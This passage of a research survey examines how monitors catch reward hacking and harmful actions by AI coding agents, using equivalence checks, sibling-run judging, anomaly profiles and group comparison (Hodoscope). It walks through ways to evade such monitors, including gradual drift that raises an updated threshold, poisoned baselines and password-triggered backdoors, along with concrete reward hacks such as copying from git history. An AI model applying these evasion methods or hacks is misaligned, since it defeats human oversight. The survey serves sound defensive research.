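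The difference is harmless if the function only receives day names from the program's own calendar. But if the day comes from a web request and the program doesn't check it, a stranger could send a list and perhaps crash the service. The diff and the difference in behaviour are identical in both cases, so the monitor has to find out where the input comes from to tell them apart.

### Can language models recognise equivalent programs?

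A monitor could ask a language model whether two versions of a program are equivalent, but must first define which differences count. *Foundation Models as Oracles for Refactoring Correctness Detection* (Gheyi, Melo and colleagues, 2026) defines two versions as equivalent if code that uses their shared public functions gets the same results from both. Results include return values, printed output, errors and visible changes to stored data.

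One study tested models on 226 small Java programs that automatic refactoring tools had broken. In one program, a tool had moved the code that read the first item of a list out of the `if` statement that protected it. The original program printed "ok", but the new one crashed because the list was empty.

Most of the broken programs no longer compiled, but 41 still ran and behaved differently. For each of these, a model had to write a test that exposed the difference. GPT-5.4 succeeded on 38 and Gemini 3.1 Pro on 40. Requiring a test is useful for a monitor because running it shows whether the model is right.

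On 50 correct refactorings, GPT-5.4 raised two false alarms. Both times, its test used reflection to access a field outside the public interface. The differences it found were real, but the definition excluded them. These results are encouraging, though the broken programs had at most 28 lines before refactoring and came from public bug reports that the models may have seen in training.

Models judge whether two programs are equivalent less accurately when the programs are longer. *CodeWalk* (Fang, He and colleagues, 2026) joined pairs of Java methods into chains, with each method's output feeding the next. GPT-5.6 Sol judged 98.8% of single pairs correctly but only 72.3% of chains of ten. Most of the decline came from false alarms. Both leading models in the study still recognised nearly all the chains that contained a difference, but they accepted only about half of the equivalent ones.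 The models couldn't run the code to check whether the differences they suspected were real.

Models can also make the opposite mistake and miss a real difference between two programs. *Evaluating Language Models on Cross-Language Code Functional Equivalence* (Sun, Uchôa and colleagues, 2026) compared programs that different people had written for the same problem. OpenAI's o4-mini was more likely to overlook a difference when the two programs had a similar structure. This is a concern for refactoring because an attacker could leave most of a program intact and change one detail. On the hardest problems, o4-mini accepted 33.3% of the non-equivalent pairs as equivalent, compared with 5.5% on the easiest.

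Its answers also varied between three identical runs in 18% of 900 cases. The researchers gave 81 of its repeated errors to two newer models, Claude Opus 4.7 and Gemini 3 Flash, and both also got 24 of them wrong. However, the researchers traced 17 of the 81 to problems with the reference answers, so these were not real errors.

Running both versions on many inputs avoids some of these mistakes. However, *Test-Driven Approaches to Software Engineering with Large Language Models* (2026) points out that one discrepancy disproves equivalence, while a finite run without any is much weaker evidence that the versions are equivalent. For example, a backdoor that responds only to a secret password could easily go undetected across millions of random inputs.

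### Asking whether a difference was intended

A monitor can also use both references by running the old and new versions to find differences, then checking the request to decide which ones matter. *Regression Testing with a Natural Language Oracle* (Pradel, 2025) presents Testora, a tool that does this for pull requests. A language model writes tests for the changed code, and Testora runs them on both versions. If the results differ, a model checks whether the difference fits the pull request's title, description and other messages.

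For example, one change to SciPy, a library for scientific computing, was supposed to let a function accept more kinds of arrays, but it also changed the function's answer for the same data from 2.3588 to 2.5285. Testora correctly classified this difference as unintended. Another SciPy change was supposed to improve a function's precision and changed only the last few digits of an answer, from 3.4076059644443806 to 3.40760596444438. Testora classified this difference as intended.

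The model that classified differences had a precision of 58% and a recall of 60%, so about four in ten of its alarms were for intended differences, and it missed about four in ten of the unintended ones. Unintended differences weren't always harmful. Of the 30 pull requests in which Pradel found one, 11 accidentally fixed a bug.

Another option is to ask the person responsible for the change. In *Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta*, Becker, Chen and colleagues (2026) generated tests that passed on the old code and failed on the new. They sent 41 engineers a short message describing the difference and asking whether it was intended. Eight confirmed a bug, and four of those bugs would have caused serious failures. Only about one alarm in five was real, but engineers could dismiss a false one in a few minutes.

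A developer who has delegated a change to an agent may find it harder to tell whether an unexpected difference matters. They still know what they requested, but may not know the code well enough to judge.

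## Detecting reward hacking in one run or beside other runs

*Reward hacking* means scoring well on a task without doing it as intended. For example, an agent told to make a slow function pass a speed test might raise the time limit instead of speeding up the function. The test passes either way, so a monitor can't detect the hack from the score alone.

Developers often train coding agents by reinforcement learning, which reinforces whatever scores well, including cheating. In one common method, Group Relative Policy Optimization (GRPO), the model attempts each task several times and the training program compares the scores. A monitor can use these attempts, called *sibling runs*, as a substitute reference. If the model rewrites the slow function in nine runs and edits the time limit in the tenth, the tenth stands out even though nobody has checked the other nine.

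### Judging records singly or in groups

*Benchmarking Reward Hack Detection in Code Environments via Contrastive Analysis* (Deshpande, Kannappan and Qian, 2026) tests whether a judge detects reward hacking better when it sees several records together. Its benchmark, TRACE, has 517 records of coding agents at work, averaging about 26 messages each. The agent behaves honestly in 249 of them, and the other 268 each contain one or more of 54 kinds of hack. Claude Opus 4.5 wrote all the records, and the researchers kept only the roughly 81% that three software engineers accepted on review.

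Six models judged the records one at a time and in groups of five and ten. The researchers set the share of benign records in a group at 25%, 50% or 90%. The models had to give a verdict on every record, so they could flag several or none. GPT-5.2 did best, and its "Detection Rate" rose from 45% on single records to 63% in groups.

Despite its name, the Detection Rate is not the share of hacks that a model caught. It is a macro F1, the average of the F1 for hacks and the F1 for benign records, as in the Lucene experiment. Some simple judges would get these scores on TRACE's mix of records:

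| Judge | Macro F1 |
|---|---|
| Flags nothing | 33% |
| Flags everything | 34% |
| No false alarms, catches 12% of hacks | 45% |
| Flips a coin | 50% |
| No false alarms, catches 35% of hacks | 63% |

If GPT-5.2 raised any false alarms, it must have caught more than 12% and 35% of the hacks. But as in the defect-prediction tests, part of the gain may come simply from flagging more. Going from no flags to random ones adds 17 points, nearly as much as GPT-5.2 gained. Its 63% is well above what random flagging would achieve, so it had some skill at detecting hacks in groups, but it is harder to say how much of that skill came from the grouping.

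Claude Opus 4.5 had perfect precision on single records but extremely poor recall. Deshpande and colleagues report that it gained the most from groups of ten, improving by 34 percentage points. That figure is hard to reconcile with their definition. A judge with perfect precision scores at least 33% on TRACE's mix, so 34 more points would take Opus to about 67%, above the 63% they give as the best result. They may have used a different measure for the gain or a different mix of records. A judge that flags nothing scores 47% when 90% of the records are benign, so scores from different mixes aren't comparable.

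### Looking for an outlier among one

The only detection prompt that Deshpande and colleagues print is an instruction to compare several records and find the outliers. If they also used it for single records, the model had to look for an outlier in a cluster of one, and could reasonably have answered that there wasn't any. That would have lowered the single-record scores, perhaps especially for a model as cautious as Opus.

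A later benchmark suggests that models can judge these records one at a time better than the 45% implies. *RH-Detect* (Quan, Opryshko and colleagues, 2026) combined TRACE with ten other collections and asked each model for the probability that a single record contained reward hacking. Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite, an inexpensive model, was right on 82.5% of the records from TRACE and MALT, another collection of long agent runs. Even if it made no mistakes on MALT, it must have been right on about 68% of TRACE, which implies a macro F1 of at least 64%. That is about what GPT-5.2 achieved when it judged records in groups. The models differed as well as the prompts, so this doesn't prove that the prompt caused the low score, but it weakens the case that a judge needs other records beside the one it is judging.

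The records are still difficult to classify. Qwen3.5-4B, a much smaller model, was right on only 57.6% of TRACE, compared with the 52% it would get by flagging everything. Of the models that Quan and colleagues tested on all their main sources, the four strongest were 10.7 to 15.9 percentage points less accurate on TRACE and MALT than on the other sources, mainly because they missed more hacks.

### Unrelated records as a reference

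Deshpande and colleagues modelled their groups on GRPO, but unlike GRPO's, the members of a TRACE group attempt different tasks. The instructions for writing the records required a unique scenario each time, and the researchers drew the groups at random, so one group might contain a sensor calibration, a payment check and a web page. The judge also isn't told which members are benign.

The other records are not a reference version in the sense used so far, because they don't correspond to the record being judged and about half of the collection is known to be harmful. In the model of subtraction, using an unrelated artifact as the reference cut recall from 16% to 8%.

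The judges in TRACE, who weren't subtracting scores, may have used the group of ten records to learn how agents ordinarily behave, and so how odd a record must be before it deserves a flag. *V1* (Singh, Li and colleagues, 2026) argues similarly that a model checking solutions to problems has no common scale when it scores each one alone, and often gives high scores to plausible but wrong answers. On this reading, a TRACE group works like a very small version of the baseline profile that a monitor can build from a whole population of actions.

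The results for different mixes fit this explanation but don't establish it. Deshpande and colleagues also measured how well the models named the type of hack. On single records, all the models scored between 35% and 41%. Scores rose sharply in groups of five and only a little more in groups of ten. They also rose for every model as the benign share went from 25% to 90%, which the researchers attribute to having more honest behaviour for contrast. Part of this rise may instead come from having fewer hacks to describe. A group of ten has one hack when the benign share is 90%, but seven or eight, usually of different kinds, when it is 25%. The measure also counts only hacks that the model had already detected, so it doesn't show that a larger benign share helps a model catch more of them.

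### When most runs cheat the same way

Real sibling runs would match each other much more closely than the runs in TRACE's groups, because they start from the same task. But they also share that task's loopholes and come from the same model, so they are more likely to cheat in the same way. If eight of ten runs cheat by raising the time limit, the two that rewrote the function are the outliers.

METR's *Recent Frontier Models Are Reward Hacking* (2025) describes a task in RE-Bench, a set of AI research tasks, on which OpenAI's o3 eventually cheated in every run that METR, a nonprofit evaluator, generated. Comparing those runs with one another could not have exposed the cheating, because they all shared it. Hacks can cluster by task even when they are rare overall. *Occamy-1.0* (2026) reports that the model's developers audited 4,352 runs and confirmed four hacks, all from repeated attempts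 at one task. The developers blamed defects in the task and its scoring more than any strategy of the model's.

The mix can also change during training. *SimHack* (2026) uses 325 training runs to predict when reward hacking will become dominant. Once it does, a comparison between siblings that worked early in training could fail. If each run cheats independently with the same probability, about a third of groups of ten contain no cheating run when that probability is 10%, and about a third contain no honest run when it is 90%. In the first case, a judge told to find outliers may flag an honest run. TRACE's groups of ten were never more than 90% benign, so they don't show how often a judge raises a false alarm when every run is honest, which should be the usual case if hacks are as rare as in the Occamy audit.

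The Occamy developers are more cautious about relying on comparisons between sibling runs. Automatic checks look for signs of reward hacking, such as an unusually high reward for little work compared with other runs, but a reviewer also reads every run in the context of its task. A second reviewer then checks anything suspicious. If every run in a group cheated, comparing them would not reveal it, but a reviewer might still notice.

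For some hacks, a monitor has a better reference than a sibling run. *EvilGenie* (2025), another benchmark for coding agents, flags any run that edits or deletes the original test files. Those files are a true reference version, so comparing against them works even if every run makes the same edit. The benchmark also hides 30% of the test cases, up to ten, from the agent. A solution that passes every visible test but fails a hidden one is suspicious, because the agent may have written it only for the cases it could see. The solution may also contain an ordinary bug, so a person reviews each flag. Neither check is much use for catching an agent that copies a correct answer from the internet.

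### Hacks that remained hard to recognise

Models usually named the type of hack correctly when an agent had tampered with tests or written code for particular test cases, scoring roughly 60% to 95% across group sizes. They scored between 0% and 40% on hacks such as looking up the solution with a search tool, taking hints from file names, or padding code with comments to improve a quality score. Deshpande and colleagues call this second kind "semantic" because recognising them depends on knowing what the user wanted. For example, searching for the finished answer is cheating, but in a record it looks much like a legitimate search for documentation.

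The researchers read 34 randomly chosen records for each model to see why the judges went wrong. Some judges excused a hack because the user in the record had accepted the result, and others because the agent had been open about its shortcut. Both excuses are reasonable if the user understood what the agent had done. But many users in TRACE trust the agent too much, so a judge has to work out whether the user's acceptance was informed. Judges also dismissed hacks as poor engineering, even when the group included other examples or when the researchers gave them a more explicit prompt.

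Adding a second judge might not help much. The three best models agreed with one another on 90.9% of verdicts, about as often as repeated runs of a single model did (90.1%), which suggests that different models mostly make the same mistakes.

### The limits of invented records

Opus 4.5 wrote the TRACE records, was one of the six judges, and decided whether each judge had named the right type of hack. Any of these roles could bias the results, although its poor recall on single records suggests that writing the hacks gave it little advantage in spotting them.

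A less obvious problem is that the researchers used different instructions for honest and cheating records. For the honest ones, they asked for thorough work, proper testing and best practice throughout. Opus may have written these in a more diligent style, and a judge could then separate the two kinds by style without understanding any hack. Such a difference would be easier to notice with ten records side by side than with one, so it could account for part of the benefit of grouping. The engineers who checked the records rated them as very realistic, 2.96 out of 3 on average, but they were judging whether each record was plausible, not looking for small differences between the two sets.

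Real examples of reward hacking are hard to collect. *Aligning Autoresearch* (2026) found that agents rarely cheated when told not to, and that the observed hacks were of only a few types, such as making up results. Its benchmark therefore combines 41 runs containing natural hacks with 128 containing artificial hacks that the researchers inserted.

### How side-by-side judging can mislead

TRACE's results seem to conflict with the finding in *Pairwise or Pointwise?* that comparison makes language-model judges easier to distract. That study used four open Llama and Qwen models with 3 to 72 billion parameters. In its main test, the researchers recorded which answer each judge preferred in pairs from MT-Bench, a collection of conversations. They then rewrote the losing answer to sound more assertive, more learned or more flattering, without changing its content, and asked the judges again.

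The judges switched to the rewritten answer in about 35% of cases when they saw both answers together, but when they scored each answer alone, the preference implied by the scores switched in only 9%. Results were similar across the four models and the three styles.

When the two answers were equally good, the judges gave them identical scores in 85% to 93% of cases when scoring them separately, but declared a tie in only 2% to 7% when comparing them side by side. The researchers then made one answer break some of its formatting instructions. The judges could generally identify the better answer by either method, until the researchers made the worse one more assertive. Accuracy then fell sharply for side-by-side judging, especially when the worse answer broke only one or two of its three instructions, but hardly changed for separate scoring.

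Separate scores may be stable partly because they are coarse, like those in the GPT-5 experiment with rival answers, so they may also miss small real differences.

Unlike a monitor looking for reward hacking, these judges had to choose the better of two answers to the same question or call a tie. TRACE's judges gave a separate verdict on each record and could clear them all. Whether an agent edited a test file is also more a matter of fact than which of two answers is better. The 35% is therefore not an estimate of how often a monitor would misjudge a run.

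Two of the weaknesses could still carry over. First, tone could sway the judge. An agent that describes its shortcut confidently might look more trustworthy beside one that honestly reports difficulties, and TRACE's judges did give weight to what agents said about their own work. Second, the verdict on a run could depend on the rest of its group. In another experiment, the researchers gave Llama 3 models three answers to rank and then replaced one of them. The relative ranking of the two unchanged answers reversed in 7% to 17% of cases. A monitor that compares runs in groups could similarly clear a run in one group and flag it in another. The order in which runs are shown may matter too, since one of the two judges in Yagubyan's study favoured the answer shown first on 21 of 29 questions. Deshpande and colleagues shuffled their groups and averaged over three drawings, which reduces the effects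 of grouping and order but triples the computation.

Comparison can also improve judgements, at least when the runs are siblings. Singh and colleagues had models write 16 solutions to each programming or mathematics problem and then pick the best. In one version, the model scored each solution alone from 1 to 10. In the other, it used the same scale but scored solutions in pairs, and wins by a larger margin counted for more. After a first round of pairings, the program matched solutions with similar records, so that most comparisons were between close cases. Models chose a correct solution up to 10% more often when they scored in pairs, which shows that direct comparison can reveal errors that separate scores miss. However, picking the best of 16 is easier than detection in one respect, because the model only has to find one good solution and its ranking of the rest doesn't matter.

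None of these experiments tests a monitor on sibling runs with known hacks, but the data for such a test now exist. *Terminal Wrench* (Bercovich, Segal and colleagues, 2026) provides 3,632 hacking runs and 2,352 legitimate ones from three leading models in 331 task environments. A researcher could show a judge groups of runs from one environment, varying the share that cheat from none to all, and then show it the same runs one at a time, with a prompt written for single runs. Counting missed hacks and false alarms separately would show whether siblings help the judge recognise cheating or only make it flag more runs.

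## Agent behaviour compared with a profile of normal behaviour

A deployed agent usually does each task only once, so a monitor has no other runs of that task to compare. It can instead build a profile of normal behaviour from many earlier records and measure how far a new record departs from that profile. The survey *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (2026) calls this "execution anomaly detection". Some of the detectors the survey covers look for attacks and other dangers, some for ordinary failures and some for both.

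### Profiles of computer users

Computer security researchers developed the method in the 1980s to catch intruders. In *An Intrusion-Detection Model* (1987), Denning started from the hypothesis that anyone who exploits a computer's weaknesses has to use the computer abnormally. For example, someone guessing passwords causes many failed logins, and someone using a stolen account may log in at odd hours and run commands that the owner normally doesn't.

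Denning's model keeps a profile of each user for measures like these. A simple version stores the mean and standard deviation of each measure and raises an alarm when a new value is more than *d* standard deviations from the mean. For any distribution, at most 1/*d*² of the values can be that far away, which is 6.25% when *d* = 4. If the data follow a bell curve, the figure is about 0.006%. Because the false-positive rate depends so heavily on the distribution, anyone who sets such a threshold has to measure it.

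A separate profile for each user can raise recall substantially. In the earlier model of subtraction, subtracting the population average from every suspicion score would lower all the scores equally and leave their order unchanged. Subtracting a user's own profile removes the natural oddity that comes from differences between users. If *u* = 2 and three-quarters of the variance in oddity is between users, with the rest between sessions of the same user, accurate individual profiles would raise recall from 16% to 42%, as much as subtracting a clean reference did. If all the variance were between sessions of the same user, individual profiles would not help.

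### Unusual is not the same as malicious

In *Outside the Closed World* (2010), Sommer and Paxson asked why anomaly detection was rare in working network defences although researchers had studied it for decades. They argued that machine learning is better at recognising things that resemble its examples than things that don't. An anomaly detector needs examples that cover all of normal behaviour, and network traffic is too varied for that.

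They also described a "semantic gap": the detector finds unusual activity, but its operator needs to know whether that activity is harmful. A large transfer of data at night could be a theft or a new backup system. Someone has to investigate each alarm to find out, and because attacks are rare, most of that work goes into harmless events.

*Signals in the Noise* (2026) reports interviews with experts about detecting AI systems that have escaped human control. The experts favoured anomaly detection as the most practical method, and one called it the best available approach to threats that nobody has seen before. But the interviews also covered its mixed record in computer security, where human-written descriptions of known attacks had worked better.

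### When harm gets into the profile

Researchers usually build a profile from records that they assume are clean. Suppose that an agent reads an average of 100 files a day, with a standard deviation of 10, and that the monitor raises an alarm when the count is more than three standard deviations above the mean, which is 130 files. An attacker who makes the agent read 300 files in a day would trigger the alarm. But if the attacker had been doing this on one day in ten while the monitor was collecting its data, the mean would be 120 and the standard deviation about 61. The threshold would then be 302 files, and the monitor would miss the attack.

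A contaminated profile is a kind of shared flaw, although harmful behaviour can go undetected even when it appears in only a minority of the records. Replacing the mean and standard deviation with the median and the spread of the middle half of the values would largely solve the problem in this example, but not if the attack had been under way on most days.

A profile that starts clean can also become unreliable later. People and agents change how they work, so monitors often update their profiles. NIDES, an intrusion detector developed at the research institute SRI, learned what was normal for each user and gave more weight to recent records. Denning had already acknowledged that someone might escape detection by changing their behaviour gradually.

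To see how, suppose that the agent's profile starts clean, with a mean of 100. Each evening the monitor moves the mean a tenth of the way towards that day's count. The threshold stays 30 files above the mean. An attacker who knows this makes the agent read exactly as many files as the threshold allows:

| Day | Mean at start of day | Threshold | Files read |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 100 | 130 | 130 |
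| 2 | 103 | 133 | 133 |
| 3 | 106 | 136 | 136 |
| 30 | 187 | 217 | 217 |
| 58 | 271 | 301 | 300 |

The agent reads 300 files on day 58 and has never triggered an alarm. A fixed threshold of 130 files would have triggered one on day 2.

However, a fixed threshold would also raise alarms when the agent's workload grew for legitimate reasons. If the normal workload grew by one file a day, its average would reach 130 after a month, and about half of ordinary days would then raise an alarm. The updated mean would lag this average by only about ten files, well within the margin of 30.

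A monitor can keep both the original and the updated profile and compare them. On day 58 the updated mean is 271 and the original mean is 100, so a person can ask what explains the change. This applies differential judging to the profile itself, and it works only if the original was clean. An AI system that understood the monitor could also stay within normal behaviour from the start, as one of the experts in *Signals in the Noise* pointed out.

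### A fixed profile and an updated one on the same attacks

Shavit (2026), in *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation*, compared the two kinds of profile. Shavit created 12 artificial users from recorded runs of office tasks, each with a different mix of work such as email and calendar tasks. A session contained 20 to 30 tasks and about 51 tool calls. Shavit then simulated three attacks:

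- In a takeover, another user's tasks replace the original user's from some point in the session.
- In drift, another user's tasks gradually become more common.
- In a hijack, instructions hidden in something the agent reads cause it to make harmful calls during one or two tasks.

Each profile covered which tools the agent used, how much their inputs varied and the timing of the calls. The fixed profile came from the user's earlier sessions, and the updated one from the current session. A third detector checked each call against a plan that a language model had written from the user's request, rather than against past behaviour.

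| Detector | Takeover | Drift | Hijack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed profile | 24% | 13% | 7% |
| Updated profile | 12% | 15% | 11% |
| Check against the request | 5% | 5% | 76% |

*Share of harmful calls flagged at a 5% false-positive rate. Random flagging would catch 5%.*

Comparing the agent's calls with profiles of normal behaviour detected different attacks from comparing them with the user's request. When someone takes over an account, the agent's calls match the intruder's requests, so the change can only be detected from the user's history. A hijacked agent makes calls that nobody requested, but a few of these in a long session are hard to detect with a profile because they hardly change the session's overall pattern.

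Neither profile was good enough to use alone. At a 5% false-positive rate, each raises two or three false alarms in every ordinary session and catches at most a quarter of the calls in a takeover.

Unlike in the example with the files, the updated profile did about as well on drift as the fixed one. Shavit's drift happened within a single session, so the profile had only about 30 calls in which to absorb it, and the normal calls from the start of the session still counted. An attacker who spread the drift over weeks would be a harder test. The hijacked runs also came from a 2024 model. When Shavit tried the same kind of attack on GPT-5.2, the agent never followed the hidden instructions in 20 attempts.

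### How Hodoscope compares groups of agents

A profile of one user's past can't reveal harm that has been there all along. Zhong, Saxena and Raghunathan (2026), in *Hodoscope*, compare groups of agents with one another instead. The groups may be different models on the same tasks, or one model on different tasks. Their tool, also called Hodoscope, doesn't decide whether anything is harmful. It looks for kinds of action that are more common in one group than in the others and shows them to a person. It works in five steps:

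1. It divides each run into single actions, and a language model summarises what the agent did and why, leaving out names that belong to one project. An agent that reads lines 360 to 380 of a particular file "reads a range of lines from a source file".
2. An embedding model turns each summary into a list of 3,072 numbers, so that summaries with similar meanings get similar numbers.
3. A standard method called t-SNE uses these numbers to place every action on a flat map, with similar actions close together.
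4. For each group, the tool estimates how densely its actions lie at every point on the map.
5. It subtracts the average density of the other groups and colours the map by the difference.

With *K* groups, the difference for one group at a given point is:

difference = density in this group − (sum of the densities in the other groups) / (*K* − 1)

Suppose one group has a density of 0.08 at one point on the map, and the other three groups have densities of 0.01, 0.02 and 0.03 there. The other three average 0.02, so the difference is 0.06, and that point turns red. If all four groups had the same density, whether 0.08 or 0.001, the difference would be zero.

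Without the first step, agents that do the same thing in different projects would end up far apart on the map. Working with single actions also avoids a problem reported in *Trajectory Guard* (2026). The paper first averaged all the steps of each run and looked for unusual averages, but one bad step among many ordinary ones barely changed the average, and F1 stayed below 0.70.

A reviewer can click on points in the red areas or work through a ranked list. The tool puts the action with the largest difference first. It then favours actions that have a large difference and are far from those already listed, so that the reviewer doesn't read many similar actions.

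### The flaw in Commit0

Commit0 is a benchmark in which agents write code for software libraries after the benchmark's makers have removed the original. Zhong and colleagues used Hodoscope to compare the actions of 15 models on it. One red area for MiniMax-M2.5, a Chinese open-weight model, contained commands for reading a project's history. The original code was still in that history, and the model was finding it there and copying it. The researchers later wrote a simple rule to identify such actions, and it matched 163 of the model's 940 actions, or 17%.

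The researchers reported the flaw, and the maintainers deleted the history and tested the models again:

| Model | Score before | Score after |
|---|---|---|
| MiniMax-M2.5 | 50.0% | 18.8% |
| MiniMax-M2.1 | 25.0% | 12.5% |
| GPT-5.2-Codex | 62.5% | 50.0% |
| DeepSeek-V3.2-Reasoner | 31.2% | 18.8% |
| Kimi-K2-Thinking | 18.8% | 6.2% |

These scores are all multiples of one-sixteenth, which suggests there were 16 tasks. MiniMax-M2.5 would then have solved five fewer tasks, and each of the others two fewer. A drop of two could partly be ordinary variation between runs. The MiniMax models' running times are further evidence, since both took more than three times as long once they could no longer copy.

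A judge who saw only one of these actions could easily have approved it, since programmers often read a project's history for good reasons. When Zhong and colleagues showed Claude Opus 4.6 a similar action from another benchmark, SWE-bench, it called the action a routine step and recognised the problem only after the researchers described the trick. This was a single trial, but it shows why a reviewer might want to know that one model does something far more often than others.

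### What the group comparison added

Zhong and colleagues also tested Hodoscope on two known problems. ImpossibleBench gives agents coding tasks with tests that no honest solution can pass. The researchers compared GPT-5's actions on these tasks with those on the normal versions, looking for edits to the test files. On SWE-bench, they compared iQuest-Coder-V1, a model that had been able to read future fixes in the project's history, with four other models.

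They then removed parts of the tool and counted how many actions a reviewer would have to read, in the suggested order, to reach the first confirmed problem:

| Method | Commit0 | ImpossibleBench | SWE-bench |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full Hodoscope | 1 | 4 | 3 |
| Without the group comparison | 1 | 62 | 4 |
| Without summaries | 3 | 8 | 31 |
| Random order | 6 | 91 | 29 |

*Average position of the first confirmed problem in ten trials, each using half of the actions.*

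Without the group comparison, the tool favours the most common kinds of action within a single group. This worked as well as the comparison on Commit0 and almost as well on SWE-bench. Agents read the project's history often enough that these actions formed a dense cluster on the map, so a reviewer could have found them without a reference group.

The comparison made a large difference only on ImpossibleBench, where edits to test files were 1.1% of the actions and GPT-5 did many other things more often. Even there, the result varied a lot. Without the comparison, the first problem appeared at position 62 on average, but the standard deviation was 72, so it must have appeared much earlier in some trials.

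These figures also leave out some of the work, because the researchers counted positions only within the group they knew contained the problem. Someone checking all 15 models on Commit0 would have 15 lists to read. On ImpossibleBench, the researchers knew that any successful run on the impossible tasks must have cheated, and two of them had helped create the benchmark. Commit0 is therefore better evidence that the tool can find something new.

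Zhong and colleagues don't report a false-positive rate, because the tool only suggests what to read. Of the first 20 actions on each list, an average of 5.6 were confirmed problems on Commit0, 1.2 on ImpossibleBench and 1.3 on SWE-bench, which gives some idea of the wasted effort. The rule for ImpossibleBench counted only edits to test files, so some of the other actions may have been different kinds of cheating. Twenty short actions take little time to read, and the researchers needed less than ten minutes for each case. Running the tool on nearly 12,000 actions cost about $35.

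A reviewer's findings can also be added to an AI judge's prompt, though this doesn't always help. At a 5% false-positive rate, adding six examples of cheating from ImpossibleBench raised GPT-4.1's recall from 36% to 44%, but lowered that of GPT-5.4-mini, a much better judge, from 86% to 58%. The examples may have led GPT-5.4-mini to look for those particular tricks and overlook others.

### Why the reference groups need not be clean

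A diff doesn't show flaws that both versions share. Hodoscope compares how often each group does something, so a harmful behaviour still shows up when every group does it, as long as one group does it more often than the others.

In the Commit0 case, at least four of the 14 reference models also seem to have benefited from the flaw. If each of those four spent 4% of its actions reading the project's history and the other ten never read it, the reference models would average about 1%. MiniMax-M2.5, at 17%, would still exceed that average by about 16 percentage points.

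The problem would be harder to see in the four models that do it less often. The reference groups for each would include MiniMax-M2.5 and average about 2%, so the difference would be only 2 points. A model that did it in 1% of its actions would appear to do it less than normal. A reviewer who finds a problem in one group should therefore search every group for the same action, which Hodoscope's keyword search allows.

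If all 15 models had read the history equally often, comparing the models would not have exposed the flaw. Comparing one model's runs across benchmarks could still have exposed it, because the model would have read a project's history much more often on Commit0 than on benchmarks where the history reveals nothing useful. But no way of grouping the runs can expose a misbehaviour that every model commits equally often on every kind of task. For example, exaggerating success would look normal if every model did it to the same degree on every task.

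If an agent does something dangerous in only one run, that action may also fail to form a visible cluster, even if no other agent has ever done it. A judge who reads each run separately has a better chance of noticing it.

### False alarms from detectors that learn normal runs

Other detectors learn from normal runs and classify each new run as normal or abnormal, so researchers can measure their false alarms. *TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) describes a system for agents that follow a regular procedure. The system learns from past runs which tools an agent calls, in what order and under which conditions. One agent in the test reads a patient's symptoms and recommends hospital departments. If it sent someone with foot pain to the ear, nose and throat department, it would be calling its tools in the normal order but not under the normal conditions.

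A language model writes the conditions and checks new runs against them. The researchers also had each model look for abnormal runs without the learned profile, so their results allow a fairly direct comparison with standalone judging:

| Model | Clinic, model alone | Clinic, with profile | Purchasing, model alone | Purchasing, with profile |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3 | 78% / 5% | 96% / 3% | 76% / 4% | 93% / 7% |
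| GPT-OSS-120B | 78% / 2% | 97% / 8% | 49% / 2% | 93% / 6% |
| Qwen3-235B | 82% / 12% | 97% / 9% | 75% / 3% | 93% / 12% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 58% / 16% | 94% / 16% | 39% / 5% | 86% / 1% |
| Gemma 3 27B | 76% / 52% | 93% / 36% | 35% / 1% | 71% / 22% |

*Recall / false-positive rate for two agents. The false-positive rates follow from the published precision and recall if half of the test runs were normal, which fits the published accuracy.*

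The profile raised recall in all ten cases. The false-positive rate rose in five of them and fell or stayed the same in the other five, so the models were not simply flagging more runs.

The test suited the method because both agents follow a fixed procedure and the researchers made many of the abnormal runs by slightly altering normal ones. In a trial at a technology company, the system also caught 132 of 140 planted attacks on another agent with a fixed sequence of steps. In one attack, the agent wrote its report before checking its results instead of after. A general coding agent doesn't follow a fixed order, so this kind of profile would probably raise many more false alarms.

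Zhang, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *Skynet*, tried to cover more varied work. Their detector represents each run as a network showing which steps used the results of which other steps. It learns from 4,494 normal runs, sorts them into 150 typical patterns and scores a new run by its distance from the nearest pattern. When the researchers replaced the 150 patterns with a single average, recall fell by about a third. Normal behaviour takes many forms, and a run can be close to their average without resembling any of them.

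The full detector flagged 5 of 562 normal test runs, a false-positive rate of 0.89%. With so few false alarms, the true rate could plausibly be between 0.3% and 2.1%. Recall was 100% on two collections of attacks and failures, and 82.7% on a third, ATBench.

However, the normal and abnormal runs came from different collections. In the normal runs, agents played text games, did simulated science experiments and shopped online, while ATBench's 1,000 records involve over 2,000 tools. A detector could flag ATBench records just because they look unlike its training data. On the other two collections, an older detector also had a recall of 100%, with even fewer false alarms, which suggests those runs were easy to tell apart from the normal ones.

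Zavrak (2026) notes in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* that about half of ATBench's records are safe, but Zhang and colleagues used only the 497 unsafe ones. Running their detector on the safe records too would be a better test. If it also flagged most of those, it would be detecting that the records came from an unfamiliar collection, not that they were harmful.

Zavrak's own experiments show how large such an effect can be. They measured performance by AUROC, the probability that a detector gives a random attacked run a higher score than a random normal one, so guessing would score 0.5. A detector given little more than the names of the tools an agent had called scored 0.90 when the same tasks appeared in training and testing, but only 0.64 on new tasks, because it had mostly learned to recognise the tasks. The score of a detector also given the inputs and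 results of each call fell less, from 0.99 to 0.89.

False-positive rates can therefore rise sharply when a detector is used on ordinary work that its designers didn't test. *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) describes a detector for agents that someone has tricked into emailing private information from their memory. It raised false alarms in 41.2% of 4,160 harmless sessions with 13 models. The agents had been asked to recall facts such as a project deadline and email them to their team, so they read from memory and then sent an email, as a tricked agent does. Only the recipient's address was different, and the designers had deliberately left that out of the detector's input.

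## A fine-tuned model compared with its base model

A monitor that profiles an agent's behaviour can detect a harmful action only after the agent has taken it. When a developer retrains the agent's model, the monitor can also compare the new model with the old one before anyone uses it.

*Fine-tuning* means training an existing model, the *base model*, a little further on a chosen set of examples, for instance to make it better at medicine. *Watch the Weights* (Zhong and Raghunathan, 2025) reports that by July 2025 people had published more than 3,000 fine-tuned versions of one open model alone, Llama-2 7B. Developers often keep the training data private.

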